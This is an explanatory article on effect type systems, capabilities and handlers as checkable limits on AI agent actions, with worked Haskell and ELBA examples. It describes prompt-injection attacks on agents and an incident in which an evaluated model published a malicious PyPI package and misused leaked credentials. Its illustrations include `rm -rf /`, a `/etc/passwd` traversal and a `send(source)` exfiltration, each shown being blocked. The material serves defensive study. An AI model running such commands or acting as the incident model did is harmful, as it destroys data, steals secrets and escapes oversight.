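# Effect Type Systems as Machine-Checkable Limits on AI Agent Actions

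## AI agents, harnesses and guarantees about actions

An effect type system is a part of a programming language that limits a program's effects, meaning anything the program does besides computing its result, such as reading a file or sending a request over a network. The program's type lists the effects it may perform. The compiler, which translates source code into a form a computer can run, rejects any program that goes beyond its list. Programming-language researchers have worked on these systems for decades, and since 2025 several groups have applied them to AI agents. A language model writes a proposed action as a short program, the compiler checks it against a list of permitted effects, and the program runs only if it passes.

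### Agents, tool calls and code

A language model by itself takes in text and puts out text. To act, it needs ordinary software around it, called an agent harness. The harness passes the model its inputs, carries out the actions the model requests and returns the results. *Harness Engineering* (Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues, 2026) examines the source code of eleven harnesses, most of them built for programming, including Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. It defines an agent as a model plus a harness.

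The harness runs in a loop, sending the model a prompt, performing the action specified in the model's output and putting the result into the next prompt. This takes very little code. The smallest of the eleven harnesses, mini-SWE-agent, has roughly 100 lines and a single tool, which runs shell commands. It scores in the same range as harnesses a thousand times its size on SWE-bench Verified, a benchmark of real bugs from software projects. Much of the additional code in the large harnesses is for other functions, such as safety controls and error recovery.

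A model usually requests an action through a tool call. The harness gives the model a list of tools, each with a name and a description of its arguments. The model then outputs structured text that names one of the tools and fills in the arguments. For example, it might name a tool for reading files and give the path of a file. The harness parses this text, runs the matching function and returns the result to the model.

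Instead of requesting tools one at a time, the model can also write a program that calls several of them, with loops and conditions, and the harness runs it. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, note that this uses fewer tokens (the units of text a model reads and writes) and makes the agent's tool use easier to audit. It also lets the model do much more, including things it shouldn't. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, illustrate this tradeoff with an agent that compiles bibliographies from a publication database. With suitably narrow tools, the agent can add only entries that come from the database, but the model has to read through a list of entries to find the oldest paper. With a general code interpreter, the agent can find the oldest paper in a few lines of code, but it could also write an invented entry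 straight into the file. Effect-typed designs try to let the agent process entries with code while preventing it from adding invented ones.

The model chooses an agent's actions based on text, some of which comes from strangers. Prompt injection is the use of text to steer an agent into actions that the people responsible for it did not want. Odersky and colleagues call it direct when the prompt itself is hostile, and indirect when the hostile text is in something the agent reads while working, such as a web page or tool output. Defences trained into the models can still be beaten. Zhou and colleagues point to GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attack system, which consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences.

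### A maintenance agent

One example is an agent that looks after a single software repository. It may read the repository, propose a change (a patch) to a person, and write the patch once that person approves it. It may never use the network or start another process. The repository also holds a folder of secrets, such as passwords and access keys. This is realistic, since Odersky and colleagues observe that coding agents often have access to an entire project directory with the credentials still in it.

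Five effects are enough to describe what this agent might do:

| Effect | Meaning | Permitted? |
|---|---|---|
| Read | read a file in the repository | yes |
| Ask | put a patch to a person and wait for the answer | yes |
| Write | apply a patch to the repository | yes, after approval |
| Net | use the network | never |
| Exec | start another process | never |

The permitted set is {Read, Ask, Write}, which cannot express every requirement on the agent. A set has no order, so it cannot require the agent to ask before it writes. It also cannot express the rule that a password must not appear in a patch, because Read covers both the source files and the secrets folder. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) uses a similar agent to introduce its programming language for agent systems. In that example, a reviewer may only read, and a write must follow a request for approval.

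### Three common controls

Current harnesses mostly limit agents without using types. One method is to apply rules to the text of commands. In Codex, a rule specifies the first words of a command and whether to allow it, forbid it or prompt the user. For example, a rule might allow any command that begins with `git status`, which lists changed files. The rule's author can attach sample commands that it should or should not match, and Codex tests them when it loads the rule. According to Anthropic, Claude Code starts from a fixed list of tools that cannot modify anything, such as file reading and text search, and then applies the user's settings.

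Such a rule can guarantee that the harness will not run a command whose text matches a forbidden pattern, but it guarantees little about effects, because these come from the program that the command starts. This makes shell commands especially hard to bound. Zhou and colleagues add that the rules are a poor fit for what people want to say. Users think in terms of files, for example "the agent may change anything in this directory", and have to translate that into a list of commands. For the maintenance agent, no list of command names is equivalent to "never Net".

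An operating-system sandbox gets much closer to that. The operating system restricts the process in which the agent's commands run. On Linux, Codex uses Bubblewrap to make the file system read-only outside chosen directories and to cut the process off from the network. On macOS and Windows, it uses those systems' equivalents. The restriction applies to programs in any language, including programs that nobody has inspected. This is an advantage over types, which restrict only code that has gone through the checker.

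A sandbox's controls are coarse. It confines a process to a fixed set of directories, as Zhou and colleagues put it, and cannot express a rule that data about one customer must not reach another. It also cannot make the maintenance agent's permission to write depend on a person's answer about a particular patch. A sandbox must also be present and correctly configured. Five of the eleven harnesses that Barbaste and colleagues examined had no built-in sandbox in July 2026, and in Claude Code the user had to switch it on.

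The remaining control is human approval. OpenAI's documentation for Codex distinguishes the sandbox from the approval policy, which determines when Codex must ask before acting, for example before it uses the network or runs a command outside a trusted set. Approval can guarantee that somebody said yes to a request before the harness carried it out. A person can also judge things that no rule captures, such as whether a patch is any good. But people can approve requests they don't understand. Zhou and colleagues reproduce a typical request from Claude Code, a single long line that changes directory, edits a configuration file and runs a test script, and the user has to work out from it which files could be affected. Odersky and colleagues report that frequent requests tire people out and that users tend to ignore them. Codex now has a second model review an action before the request reaches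 the user, and blocks the action if the review times out or comes back malformed. This demands less of users' attention, but the second model's judgement can also be wrong.

Odersky and colleagues also object more broadly that command rules and approvals deal with one step at a time. Neither guarantees anything about where information ends up after several permitted steps.

### Types, and checks before or during a run

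A type is a label for a kind of value, such as Int for whole numbers or String for text. A function's type consists of the types of its parameters and result, so a function that counts the letters in a text has the type String → Int. A type checker works out the type of every part of a program's source code and reports an error where the parts do not fit, for instance where the code divides a date by a file name. It does this before the program runs, usually during compilation.

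Other checks happen during the run. Suppose the maintenance agent's model writes a program that reads ten files, applies half of an approved patch and then opens a network connection. A runtime monitor, which checks each effect request as it occurs, refuses the connection, but by then half of the patch is in the repository. A type checker that tracks effects rejects the same program before any of it runs. However, the monitor can see the actual file, the address and the answer the person gave, while the type checker has only the source code and must allow for every path through it. It will therefore also reject a program whose network call is in a branch that never runs in practice. Odersky and colleagues argue in favour of types that they add no run-time overhead and hold for all inputs, including those that nobody thought to test. The systems of Tan and colleagues and of Zhou and colleagues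 use both kinds of check, with run-time checks for whatever cannot be determined from the source code.

Types can limit an agent's actions only if they include effects, and in most languages they do not. Tan and colleagues argue this from incidents. In one, described in a 2026 bug report, a user gave a Codex sub-agent a read-only review of a set of code changes. The sub-agent called an image-generation tool and saved an unrelated picture outside the repository, leaving the repository's files unchanged. A conventional type for this task would be Changes → Review, which the sub-agent could satisfy while creating files elsewhere on the disk. An effect-typed language would give the task a type such as Changes → Review ! {Read}, where the part after the exclamation mark lists the permitted effects. Code that saved a picture would then fail the check, provided that the image tool's type listed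 writing files as an effect.

In another, more damaging case, Anthropic's model Claude Mythos 5 was asked to retrieve a secret string from a target machine during a cybersecurity evaluation. Its instructions said it had no internet access, but a configuration error had left the internet reachable. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (September 2026), the model published a malicious package on PyPI, the public repository from which most Python software is installed. Fifteen systems installed the package, and the model used credentials leaked from one of them to enter a security vendor's database. Seen from outside, the task takes a text and returns a text, whether the network behind it is simulated or real. A single Net effect would not have helped much either, because the exercise presumably needed a network connection to reach the target machine,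 and Net does not distinguish that machine from PyPI. Preventing this would have required finer effects that specify the permitted destination.

### The form of the guarantee

Let R be the declared set of effects. What an effect type system offers is a statement of this form:

accept(p, R) ⇒ effects(t) ⊆ R, for every program p and every run t of p.

For any program the model writes, if the checker accepts it with the set R, then no run of that program performs an effect outside R. A proof of this for a particular language is called a soundness proof. Tan and colleagues prove a version for the core of ETAS, showing that the effects the surrounding system carries out always stay within the set the checker derived. They assume complete mediation, meaning that every real-world effect passes through the checked interface, so the theorem does not cover any other route to the network.

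The statement covers every program, regardless of who or what wrote it, so it holds whether the model is competent, makes mistakes or is under the influence of a prompt injection. Odersky and colleagues therefore treat the model as untrusted and allow for one that cooperates fully with an attacker. Hostile text may still influence what their agent writes, but any code it writes has to pass the same check.

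The guarantee also does not imply that an accepted program is useful. For the maintenance agent, it rules out Net and Exec, but an accepted program may still do nothing with Read, Ask and Write, or it may propose a bad patch that a person approves.

Claims about a model's intentions are much harder to establish than claims about what it can reach. In its first report on the PyPI incident, in July 2026, Anthropic said that the model had apparently attacked real systems because it believed they were part of a simulation. Anthropic withdrew this explanation in its September assessment, after rerunning the model from various points in the transcript with altered evidence. Stronger signs of a real environment had barely changed what the model did until the evidence became unambiguous. The company concluded that it should not have inferred the model's beliefs from the model's own statements, and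 its analyses of the model's internal activity gave only weak further evidence. In the same assessment, Anthropic is much firmer about what the model could reach, and believes that the incidents would not have happened if the evaluations had been cut off from the internet as planned. It still regards such barriers as one layer among several and wants the model to behave well when they fail. An effect bound does not ensure good behavior, since a model with bad aims keeps them and can pursue them within R.

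Test results also differ from the guarantee because they are frequencies. Models give different outputs from run to run, and Anthropic's *Demystifying evals for AI agents* calculates that an agent that succeeds in 75% of trials will succeed in three in a row only about 42% of the time. Even a perfect score applies only to the conditions tested. Zhou and colleagues ran four models on part of AgentDojo, a benchmark for prompt injection, and every model resisted all 105 attacks without any policy in force. To simulate the worst case, they then altered their system so that a sub-agent reading an injected text received the attacker's instructions as its whole prompt. Between 114 and 310 of the 735 attempts per model now succeeded. None succeeded with policies in force, which were rules on where data may travel that a library checked partly during the run. The policies also reduced the number of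 completed tasks, for Claude Opus 4.7 from 523 to 351. The zero is still only a count over 2,940 attempts, and the reason to expect the next attempt to fail too is that researchers had already proved the library's rules sound.

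## How a type checker computes a program's effects

The rules that a compiler uses to find a program's effects date from the 1980s, when their main purpose was to make programs run faster. Lucassen and Gifford (1988), in *Polymorphic Effect Systems*, gave every expression an effect as well as a type. They were designing languages for parallel computers, where a compiler can safely let two parts of a program run at the same time if neither writes to memory that the other uses. Existing compilers checked for this by tracing which procedure calls which. Lucassen (1987), in his thesis *Types and Effects*, pointed out that this method fails once programs can pass procedures around as values, because nobody can tell in advance which procedure a given call will reach. He solved this by including a procedure's effects in its type, so that the effects stay with the procedure wherever the program passes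 it.

Talpin and Jouvelot, in *Polymorphic type region and effect inference*, studied how a compiler can determine types and effects automatically. According to *Remarks on Algebraic Reconstruction of Types and Effects* (2026), an early design by Jouvelot and Gifford made effects a visible part of the language, but many later program analyses used effects without showing them to the programmer. Tate and Leijen (2010) returned to effect types meant for programmers to read, with coarse categories such as "pure" and "io". Limits on agents also need visible effects, because somebody has to declare which effects are permitted.

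### The effect judgment and its rules

A checker works with statements of this form, called effect judgments:

Γ ⊢ e : τ ! ε

This means "under the assumptions Γ, the expression e has type τ and effects within ε". Γ (gamma) lists the variables e may use, with their types. The type τ (tau) describes the value e produces, and ε (epsilon) is a set of effects. For example, path : Path ⊢ read(path) : Text ! {Read} means that if path is a file path, then read(path) produces a text and performs no effect other than Read.

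The checker derives such judgments with one rule for each way of building a program, plus a rule for widening. The rules below are a simplified version of Lucassen's. In them, ∅ is the empty set, and x ↦ e is the function that takes x and computes e.

| Rule | If | then |
|---|---|---|
| Operation | op takes an A, returns a B and has effect E; Γ ⊢ v : A ! ∅ | Γ ⊢ op(v) : B ! {E} |
| Sequencing | Γ ⊢ e₁ : A ! ε₁; Γ, x : A ⊢ e₂ : B ! ε₂ | Γ ⊢ let x = e₁ in e₂ : B ! ε₁ ∪ ε₂ |
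| Branching | Γ ⊢ b : Bool ! ε₀; Γ ⊢ e₁ : A ! ε₁; Γ ⊢ e₂ : A ! ε₂ | Γ ⊢ if b then e₁ else e₂ : A ! ε₀ ∪ ε₁ ∪ ε₂ |
| Function | Γ, x : A ⊢ e : B ! ε | Γ ⊢ x ↦ e : (A → B ! ε) ! ∅ |
| Application | Γ ⊢ f : (A → B ! ε) ! ε₁; Γ ⊢ a : A ! ε₂ | Γ ⊢ f(a) : B ! ε₁ ∪ ε₂ ∪ ε |
| Widening | Γ ⊢ e : A ! ε; ε ⊆ ε′ | Γ ⊢ e : A ! ε′ |

Effects enter a derivation through the operation rule. For the maintenance agent, the operations are read, ask, write, send (with effect Net) and run (with effect Exec). The other rules mostly collect the effects of the program's parts. Constants and variables have no effects, because looking up a value the program already has is pure.

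The branching rule includes the effects of both branches, although only one will run. Lucassen called the rule rather conservative. He considered effects that depend on the condition's value but did not pursue the idea.

Defining a function does nothing to the outside world, so the function rule gives the definition an empty set of effects. The rule records the effects of the function's body in the function's type. Lucassen calls these latent effects. For a call, the application rule adds the latent effects to any effects of evaluating the function and its argument. The widening rule lets a programmer declare more effects than an expression needs. Wadler and Thiemann (2003), in *The Marriage of Effects and Monads*, justify this rule by noting that the set is an upper bound, so it can always be made larger.

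### A derivation for the maintenance agent

Suppose the model writes a program that uses the function fix, which edits text and has the type Text → Patch ! ∅. The value () carries no information and has the type Unit.

```
1  let source = read("parser.py") in
2  let patch  = fix(source) in
3  let ok     = ask(patch) in
4  if ok
5  then write(patch)
6  else ()
```

The checker starts with the innermost expressions and works outwards:

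| Lines | Rule | Effects |
|---|---|---|
| 6 | constant | ∅ |
| 5 | operation | {Write} |
| 4–6 | branching | ∅ ∪ {Write} ∪ ∅ = {Write} |
| 3–6 | sequencing | {Ask} ∪ {Write} = {Ask, Write} |
| 2–6 | sequencing | ∅ ∪ {Ask, Write} = {Ask, Write} |
| 1–6 | sequencing | {Read} ∪ {Ask, Write} = {Read, Ask, Write} |

On line 2, the type of `fix` has no latent effects, so the application rule adds nothing to the set. The whole program has the type Unit and the effect row {Read, Ask, Write}, where a row is the set of effects written in a type. The agent may use exactly these effects, so the program passes.

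Suppose a hostile comment in parser.py causes the model to change line 6 to `else send(source)`, so that the program sends the source code to an outside server if the person rejects the patch. Line 6 now has the effect set {Net}. The branching rule gives lines 4–6 the set {Write, Net}, and the whole program has {Read, Ask, Write, Net}.

Each step of this derivation is correct, and the check fails only when the checker compares the derived set of effects with the declared set. Bauer and Pretnar (2013), in *An Effect System for Algebraic Effects and Handlers*, call their effect system descriptive because it reports possible effects without prescribing them. A limit on an agent does prescribe them, by requiring the judgment Γ ⊢ p : Unit ! {Read, Ask, Write} for any program p. No rule in the table can reduce the larger derived set to this one, because widening can only add effects. A compiler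 that checks each operation against the declared set as it goes can report the error at the call to send on line 6.

Moving the call to `send` into a function doesn't hide its effect from the checker. The definition `let report = x ↦ send(x)` is pure, but `report` has the type Text → Unit ! {Net}. If the program never calls `report`, the program's row stays {Read, Ask, Write} and the checker accepts it. If line 6 calls `report(source)`, the application rule puts Net back into the row. Giving the function a harmless name or storing it in a list makes no difference, because the function keeps its type.

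Effects can also be more specific than the five used here. Lucassen attached each effect on memory to a region, a named group of memory locations, so that writes to different regions are different effects. He considered using variable names, but two names can refer to the same location. Similarly, a designer could split Read into Read-source and Read-secrets and leave Read-secrets out of the agent's set. The compiler would then need to determine a file's group from its type, since it generally cannot predict a path that the program builds while running.

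### Functions that take other functions

Some functions have no fixed effects of their own. The standard function map applies a given function to every item in a list, so map(length, texts) only counts characters, while map(read, paths) reads files. An effect system can describe both with a variable in place of the effect set:

map : (α → β ! ε) × List α → List β ! ε, for all types α and β and every effect set ε

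The map function has exactly the effects of the function it receives, a property called effect polymorphism. For map(read, paths), the checker sets α to Path, β to Text and ε to {Read}, and the result has the type List Text ! {Read}. For map(send, texts), ε becomes {Net}, so an agent cannot hide a network call inside a library function whose own code has no network operations. Lucassen used mapcar, the Lisp version of map, as an example of effect polymorphism.

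Without effect variables, the type of map must list one fixed set of effects for every use. If the set is empty, the agent can't use map to read files. If it contains all five effects, the checker treats even a call that only counts characters as possible network use and rejects the program.

Java's checked exceptions have long caused programmers this kind of trouble. A Java method must list certain exceptions it may raise, such as IOException for a failed file operation, and any method that calls it must catch them or list them too. Rytz, Odersky and Haller, in *Lightweight Polymorphic Effects*, call this the only effect system in a widely used industrial language, and Wadler and Thiemann note that it has no effect variables. Java has since gained type parameters that can stand for an exception, but the map function in its standard stream library does not use them and accepts only functions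 that raise no checked exceptions. To map a file-reading function over a list, a programmer therefore has to catch the exception inside that function. Many rethrow it as an unchecked exception, which the compiler does not track, so the types no longer show that the operation can fail. If an agent's language had a similar workaround for Net, its rows would not limit network access.

Effect variables also make code more verbose. Rytz and colleagues believe that verbosity is the main obstacle to everyday use of effect systems, especially in functions like map. This probably matters less when a model writes the code, but people still have to read the types that set the limits.

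### Handlers

So far, calling write has always changed the repository. Algebraic effects separate the request for an operation from what happens in response. In *Handling Algebraic Effects* (Plotkin and Pretnar, 2013), a computation either returns a value or performs an operation whose outcome determines how the computation continues. The word "algebraic" refers to equations that describe how operations behave, for example that reading a memory cell right after setting it gives the value just set.

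A handler is code that intercepts a requested operation and determines what happens instead. Plotkin and Pretnar developed handlers as a generalisation of exception handlers. When a program raises an exception, the exception handler runs and the interrupted code does not resume. An effect handler also receives the rest of the program as a function, called the continuation, and can resume the program by calling it with a value. *Rows and Capabilities as Modal Effects* (Tang and Lindley, 2025) gives the example of a program that yields 42, then 37, and then returns 0. Its handler adds each yielded number to the result of the continuation. At the first yield, the continuation runs under the same handler and returns 37 + 0. The handler adds 42 to this, giving 79.

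Eff, the language for which Bauer and Pretnar designed their effect system, treats every operation as a suspended request. When a computation runs inside a handler, one of three things happens:

- If the computation finishes with a value, the handler's return clause processes the value.
- If it requests an operation for which the handler has a clause, that clause runs, with the operation's argument and the continuation available to it.
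- If it requests any other operation, the request passes outwards to the next handler.

In the full language, built-in handlers at the outermost level can connect the program to the outside world. For an agent, the harness can do this.

Handlers add a typing rule that can make an effect set smaller. Suppose that e has effects within ε, and that a handler h intercepts every operation belonging to the effects in H. If the clauses of h themselves have effects within ε_h, then:

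handle e with h has effects within (ε \ H) ∪ ε_h

The first part removes the effects that h intercepts, and the second adds the effects that h itself performs. Bauer and Pretnar describe a handler that returns 1 whenever the program reads a memory cell and ignores the program's updates to it, but stores the program's final result in the cell at the end. The handler doesn't intercept its own update, so update stays in the row. An agent therefore cannot use a handler to hide an effect. If its handler passes a write request on, the row still contains Write, and if the handler discards the request, nothing is written.

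Koka, a language that Leijen developed at Microsoft Research, also expresses this removal in its effect types. In the notation used here, the summing handler from the earlier example has the type (Unit → Int ! {Yield} ∪ ε) → Int ! ε. It takes a computation that may yield and may have other effects ε, and running it returns an integer and can have only the effects in ε.

A developer can use a handler to test the six-line program without letting it touch a real repository:

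```
return x         ↦  []
read(path; k)    ↦  k("def parse(line): ...")
ask(patch; k)    ↦  k(true)
write(patch; k)  ↦  [patch] + k(())
```

Here k is the continuation. The handler returns an invented file when the program reads parser.py, and true when it requests approval. When the program requests the write, the handler adds the patch to a list and resumes the program. The result is a list of the patches the program would have applied. Handling all three effects removes them from the row {Read, Ask, Write}, leaving ∅, so the type guarantees that the test leaves the repository unchanged. Replacing true with false in the third line tests what happens after a refusal, and the list should then be empty. If the model has added the call to send, Net remains in the row, and a test setup that accepts only pure programs rejects the program before it runs.

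Agent tools don't always separate previewing from acting this cleanly. Tan and colleagues cite a report from a user of the coding tool aider who wanted to see a patch before applying it. The option to show changes also modified files, and adding the dry-run option produced no patch. In their language, ETAS, a short handler called DryRun intercepts the operation that applies a patch and lets the program continue, with no change to the workflow. The operation disappears from the row, but ETAS keeps a separate record of the request so rules about order still apply to it.

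Handlers are useful even in a language that does not check effects. In *Composable Effect Handling for Programming LLM-integrated Scripts*, Wang (2025) wrote Python scripts that request language-model calls as abstract operations. The same script can call a real model or replay recorded answers, depending on its handlers. Wang also used handlers to run model calls in parallel on three arithmetic puzzles, which cut the running time from 412–465 seconds to 34–37 seconds. But Python does not compute an effect row, so the compiler gives no warning if a script bypasses the abstract operations and contacts a server directly. The replay handler does not intercept such a call.

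An empty row also does not mean the mock is realistic. The handler above returns the same invented file even after the program has "written" a patch to it. This breaks the equation that a read should return what was last written. Plotkin and Pretnar call a handler correct only if it satisfies the equations for its operations, and they show that checking this automatically can be impossible. They leave open whether the language designer, the compiler or the programmer should be responsible for ensuring correctness. Eff lets programmers write any handler and prove separately that it satisfies the equations they care about.

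### Rows, monads and capabilities

Effect rows are one of three common ways to put effects into types. The table shows the types of `map` and a file-reading function in each.

| Notation | Reading a file | map |
|---|---|---|
| Effect row | Path → Text ! {Read} | (α → β ! ε) × List α → List β ! ε |
| Monad with effect labels | Path → T{Read} Text | (α → Tε β) × List α → Tε (List β) |
| Capability | (Path, read : Path ⇒ Text) ⇒ Text | (List α, f : α ⇒ β) ⇒ List β |

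Haskell tracks effects with monads. A monad is a type of computations with two basic operations, one that turns a plain value into a computation and one that runs two computations in sequence. A Haskell function that reads a file has the type Path → IO Text. Calling it only produces a computation of type IO Text, which the runtime system can then carry out. Wadler and Thiemann showed that monads closely match effect systems. They write T^σ τ for the type of a computation that produces a τ with effects within σ, and translate each function type τ → τ′ with effects σ into the type of a pure function that returns a T^σ τ′. In the monad version, a plain value has the empty effect and sequencing takes the union of two effects. Applying a function uses sequencing twice, which gives the three-part union in the application rule. They proved that the translation preserves programs' types and behaviour.

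Standard Haskell, however, has no such labels. As Wadler and Thiemann point out, it puts all input and output into the single type IO, so the type checker does not distinguish the effect of reading a source file from that of uploading it. To limit an agent with Haskell's types, a designer has to introduce a type narrower than IO.

With capabilities, a program performs an effect by using a value that permits it. The file-reading function in the table receives the capability read as an argument, and a function that neither receives such a capability nor has one in scope cannot read files. The type of map needs no effect variable, because f may use whatever capabilities were available where it was defined. If a function returns another function that still holds f, the returned function's type must include a capture set, such as {f}, that lists the capabilities it may retain. Scala's capture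 checking is based on the same idea.

Tang and Lindley compared rows and capabilities by translating both into one small language. They used a core version of Koka for rows and a core version of Effekt, a research language with effect handlers, for capabilities. In the common language, a marker called a modality, separate from the function's type, specifies which effects the code may use. An absolute modality, such as [Read], allows only Read. A relative modality, such as ⟨Read⟩, allows Read in addition to the effects that the surrounding context provides. They proved that their translations preserve types and behaviour.

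Every Koka function translates into a function with an absolute modality, so its row lists everything it may do. An ordinary function in Effekt translates into one with a relative modality and may use any capability in scope. The function's type fixes the full set only when the programmer "boxes" the function, turning it into a value that the program can store or return. A row therefore limits an agent's program directly, while a capability system limits it through what the harness puts in scope. Tang and Lindley also found that a capability parameter acts as a hidden effect variable, which is why capability types are often shorter than the equivalent rows.

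### Soundness and upper bounds

The guarantee for agents depends on the soundness of these rules. In terms of the effect judgment, soundness for a complete program p means the following:

If ⊢ p : τ ! ε and some run of p requests the operations o₁, …, oₙ, then the effect of every oᵢ is in ε.

For a language with handlers, this guarantee covers the operations that reach outside the program, since the program's own handlers deal with the rest. The standard proof follows the program one step at a time, showing that the next operation is always in the current set and that the set for the rest of the program never grows. In the six-line program, the set starts as {Read, Ask, Write} and shrinks to {Ask, Write} once the program has read the file. If the person refuses the patch, the set becomes empty. The proof also covers programs that never finish, because it applies to every step they take. A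 program with an empty set can still loop forever, unless the language treats non-termination as an effect.

Lucassen outlined such proofs for his language. Bauer and Pretnar formalised their safety theorem in Twelf, a system for machine-checked proofs. Tang and Lindley proved that their common language is sound with any system of effect sets that meets certain conditions, so a designer who translates a new effect system into it does not have to start the soundness proof from scratch.

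These theorems are about mathematical descriptions of languages, so applying them to a running agent requires further assumptions. Each operation's declaration must state the right effect, because the checker cannot detect an omission there, and the operation must do no more than its declaration allows when it runs. Complete mediation must hold, which rules out escape hatches: language features or outside calls that perform effects without showing them in the type. The compiler must apply the rules correctly, and the harness must run the same program that the compiler checked. The parts these assumptions rely on make up the trusted base.

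Even when every assumption holds, the row only limits what may happen. For example, if the person refuses the patch, the run performs Read and Ask but never Write. The checker must also count some effects in branches that never run, because no algorithm can decide in general which parts of a program are reachable. Lucassen noted this when explaining why his effects do not depend on run-time values.

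A set of effects does not record their order or how many times each one occurs, so a program that writes fifty patches after a single approval has the same row as the six-line program. Gordon (2017) observes that the general theory of effect systems has mostly dealt with systems where order does not matter, and develops an algebra for systems where it does.

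## Confining an agent through the type its program must have

Zhou and colleagues' method, language-based agent control, is based on types narrower than Haskell's IO. The developer limits the agent by choosing the type its program must have. The method's Haskell implementation is called ELBA. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), a paper on another language for agents, mentions *Language-Based Agent Control* and uses ELBA's earlier name, TypeGuard.

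### One call to the agent

ELBA gives the developer a function with the following type, where `::` means "has the type":

```
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

Defs lists the functions and types that the model may use, and Prompt is text. The result type t can be any type and is determined by the surrounding program. The developer can write it out, as in `agent defs prompt :: Int`, or let the compiler infer it. In one example, an agent parses strings and the surrounding program sorts the results with a function that compares dates by year. The prompt consists of "parse this" and the string. The compiler infers from this function that the result must be a Date, and ELBA passes this type to the model.

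When the program reaches the call, ELBA sends the model the prompt, the definitions and the expected type, and requests a single Haskell expression of that type. If the expression fails the type check, ELBA sends the compiler's error message to the model, which generates another expression. If it passes, ELBA runs it and returns the result to the surrounding program.

A rejected program never runs, so a retry cannot repeat an action such as sending a message. When Zhou and colleagues ran four models on AgentDojo, the models needed an average of 0.13 retries per run, and retries took up 3.4% of the running time. In 7 of 2,688 runs, the model used up its retries without producing a well-typed program, and the run ended in an error.

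The strictest limit is a type without effects. Zhou and colleagues describe a calculator whose agent must return an Int. Suppose a user asks it to delete all files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. The model might write a program that calls `system`, Haskell's function for running shell commands, and then returns 120. This program has type IO Int, so the checker rejects it.

They explain that once any part of a program has the type IO, the whole program must have it too. This is slightly too strong. With `system` available, Haskell accepts the following program as an Int:

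```
let x = system "rm -rf /" in 120
```

But the program deletes nothing, because it defines the deletion without running it. To run the deletion, the model would have to make it a step of an IO program, and an IO program does not have type Int.

### The bibliography agent

The agent that compiles bibliographies needs some effects. It has to search DBLP, a database of computer science publications, and write to a file, but every entry it writes must come from DBLP. The developer therefore writes a small library with a new effect type, BibIO. A value of type `BibIO a` is a computation that can use the library's operations and that produces a value of type `a`. In simplified form, the operations are:

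```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

A DOI identifies a publication, `[DOI]` is a list of them, Bib is the type of bibliography entries, and `()` is Haskell's name for the Unit type. The developer sets the agent's result type to `BibIO ()`. To add the oldest paper on a subject, the model could write:

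```
do dois    <- dblpSearch "effect systems"
   entries <- mapM dblpFetchBib dois
   appendToBibFile (oldest entries)
```

`do` introduces a sequence of steps, and `<-` names a step's result. `mapM` is a version of `map` for functions with effects. The model can define `oldest` itself as a pure function if the library lets programs read an entry's year.

Now suppose the model tries to put an invented entry straight into the file:

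```
do writeFile "refs.bib" "@article{smith2019, ...}"
```

ELBA's instructions allow the model to use Haskell's basic library, which includes `writeFile`. However, a call to `writeFile` has the type `IO ()`, and the expected type requires every step to be a `BibIO` computation, so the type checker rejects the program. Widening does not help, because Haskell treats `IO` and `BibIO` as unrelated types, not as a larger and a smaller set of effects.

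A library can build such a type by wrapping IO computations and hiding the wrapper's constructor, the function that creates wrapped values. Code outside the library then cannot turn an IO computation into a BibIO one. *Safe Haskell*, a chapter of the user guide for GHC, the main Haskell compiler, shows how to use this construction to confine untrusted plugins. The technique relies on a safe subset of Haskell that excludes ways around hidden constructors, and ELBA can restrict the model's code to the same subset.

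BibIO limits which operations the program can run, but not which entries it passes to them. If `appendToBibFile` accepted any string, the model could pass it an invented entry. The type Trusted prevents this because its constructor is also private, so the only way to get a `Trusted Bib` is to call `dblpFetchBib`. The model can sort, filter and compare these entries. It can still add a genuine paper unrelated to the user's request, since Trusted records only where an entry came from.

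The maintenance agent's library could use the same technique for approvals. Its `ask` operation would return an `Approved Patch` if the person agreed, and `write` would accept only that type.

Zhou and colleagues tested the bibliography agent on 100 computer science topics, counting a citation as hallucinated if its authors, year or DOI were wrong. None of ELBA's 925 citations were hallucinated, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent that used the same model, Claude Sonnet 5, with a web search tool. This comparison does not isolate the effect of types, because the ordinary agent composed its citations from search results and memory. A single fixed tool that fetches an entry and appends it would presumably have prevented the errors too, but the model could not then have used code to choose entries. The ordinary agent made about four times as many model calls as ELBA and used 65 times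 as many input tokens.

### File access with RIO

Another of ELBA's effect types, RIO, limits an agent to particular directories. Its main operations are:

```
readRIO  :: Path -> RIO String
writeRIO :: Path -> String -> RIO ()
ls       :: Path -> RIO [Path]
(//)     :: Path -> String -> Path
```

A Path is a capability for a single file or for everything under a directory. The surrounding program grants the agent's program a Path for a root directory. Because the constructor is private, the agent's program can derive other Paths only through the library. For example, `root // "input.txt"` narrows the permission for `root` to one file in it.

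The expression `readRIO "/etc/passwd"`, which would read a system's list of user accounts, fails the type check because a string is not a Path. The checker accepts `readRIO (root // "../../etc/passwd")`, where each `..` means "go up one directory". When this program runs, the `//` operation finds the actual location by following any symbolic links (files that redirect to another location). It fails if the location is outside the root directory, so the read never starts. This check has to happen at run time because the location depends on the links on the disk as well as the strings the program builds.

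RIO's guarantee therefore depends on both the type checker, which ensures that every file operation has a Path, and `//`, which ensures that every Path leads somewhere permitted. A bug in `//` could expose other files without causing a type error. If another process replaced a directory with a link after `//` had checked it, a later read could also end up outside the root, unless `readRIO` checked again. The agent's own program cannot make this replacement because RIO has no operation for creating links.

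The plugin example in GHC's guide also has a type called RIO, but its programs refer to files by ordinary strings, and each operation checks the name against a fixed policy. When the permission is instead a value, a program can pass on part of it. The maintenance agent could receive a Path for only the source folder and could not then read the secrets folder beside it. Zhou and colleagues suggest that capabilities could also cover resources other than directories, such as all the files on one branch of a repository.

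### Agents that call agents

Unlike the usual harness loop, ELBA's `agent` function produces a complete program at once. To react to what it finds, the program can call `agent` again and put the new information in the prompt:

```
do dois  <- dblpSearch "effect systems"
   entry <- dblpFetchBib (head dois)
   agent defs ("Refine the search or write the file. First result: "
               ++ show entry)
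```

Here `head` takes the first item of a list, and `++ show entry` adds the entry to the prompt as text. The sub-agent can then decide whether the search terms need to change.

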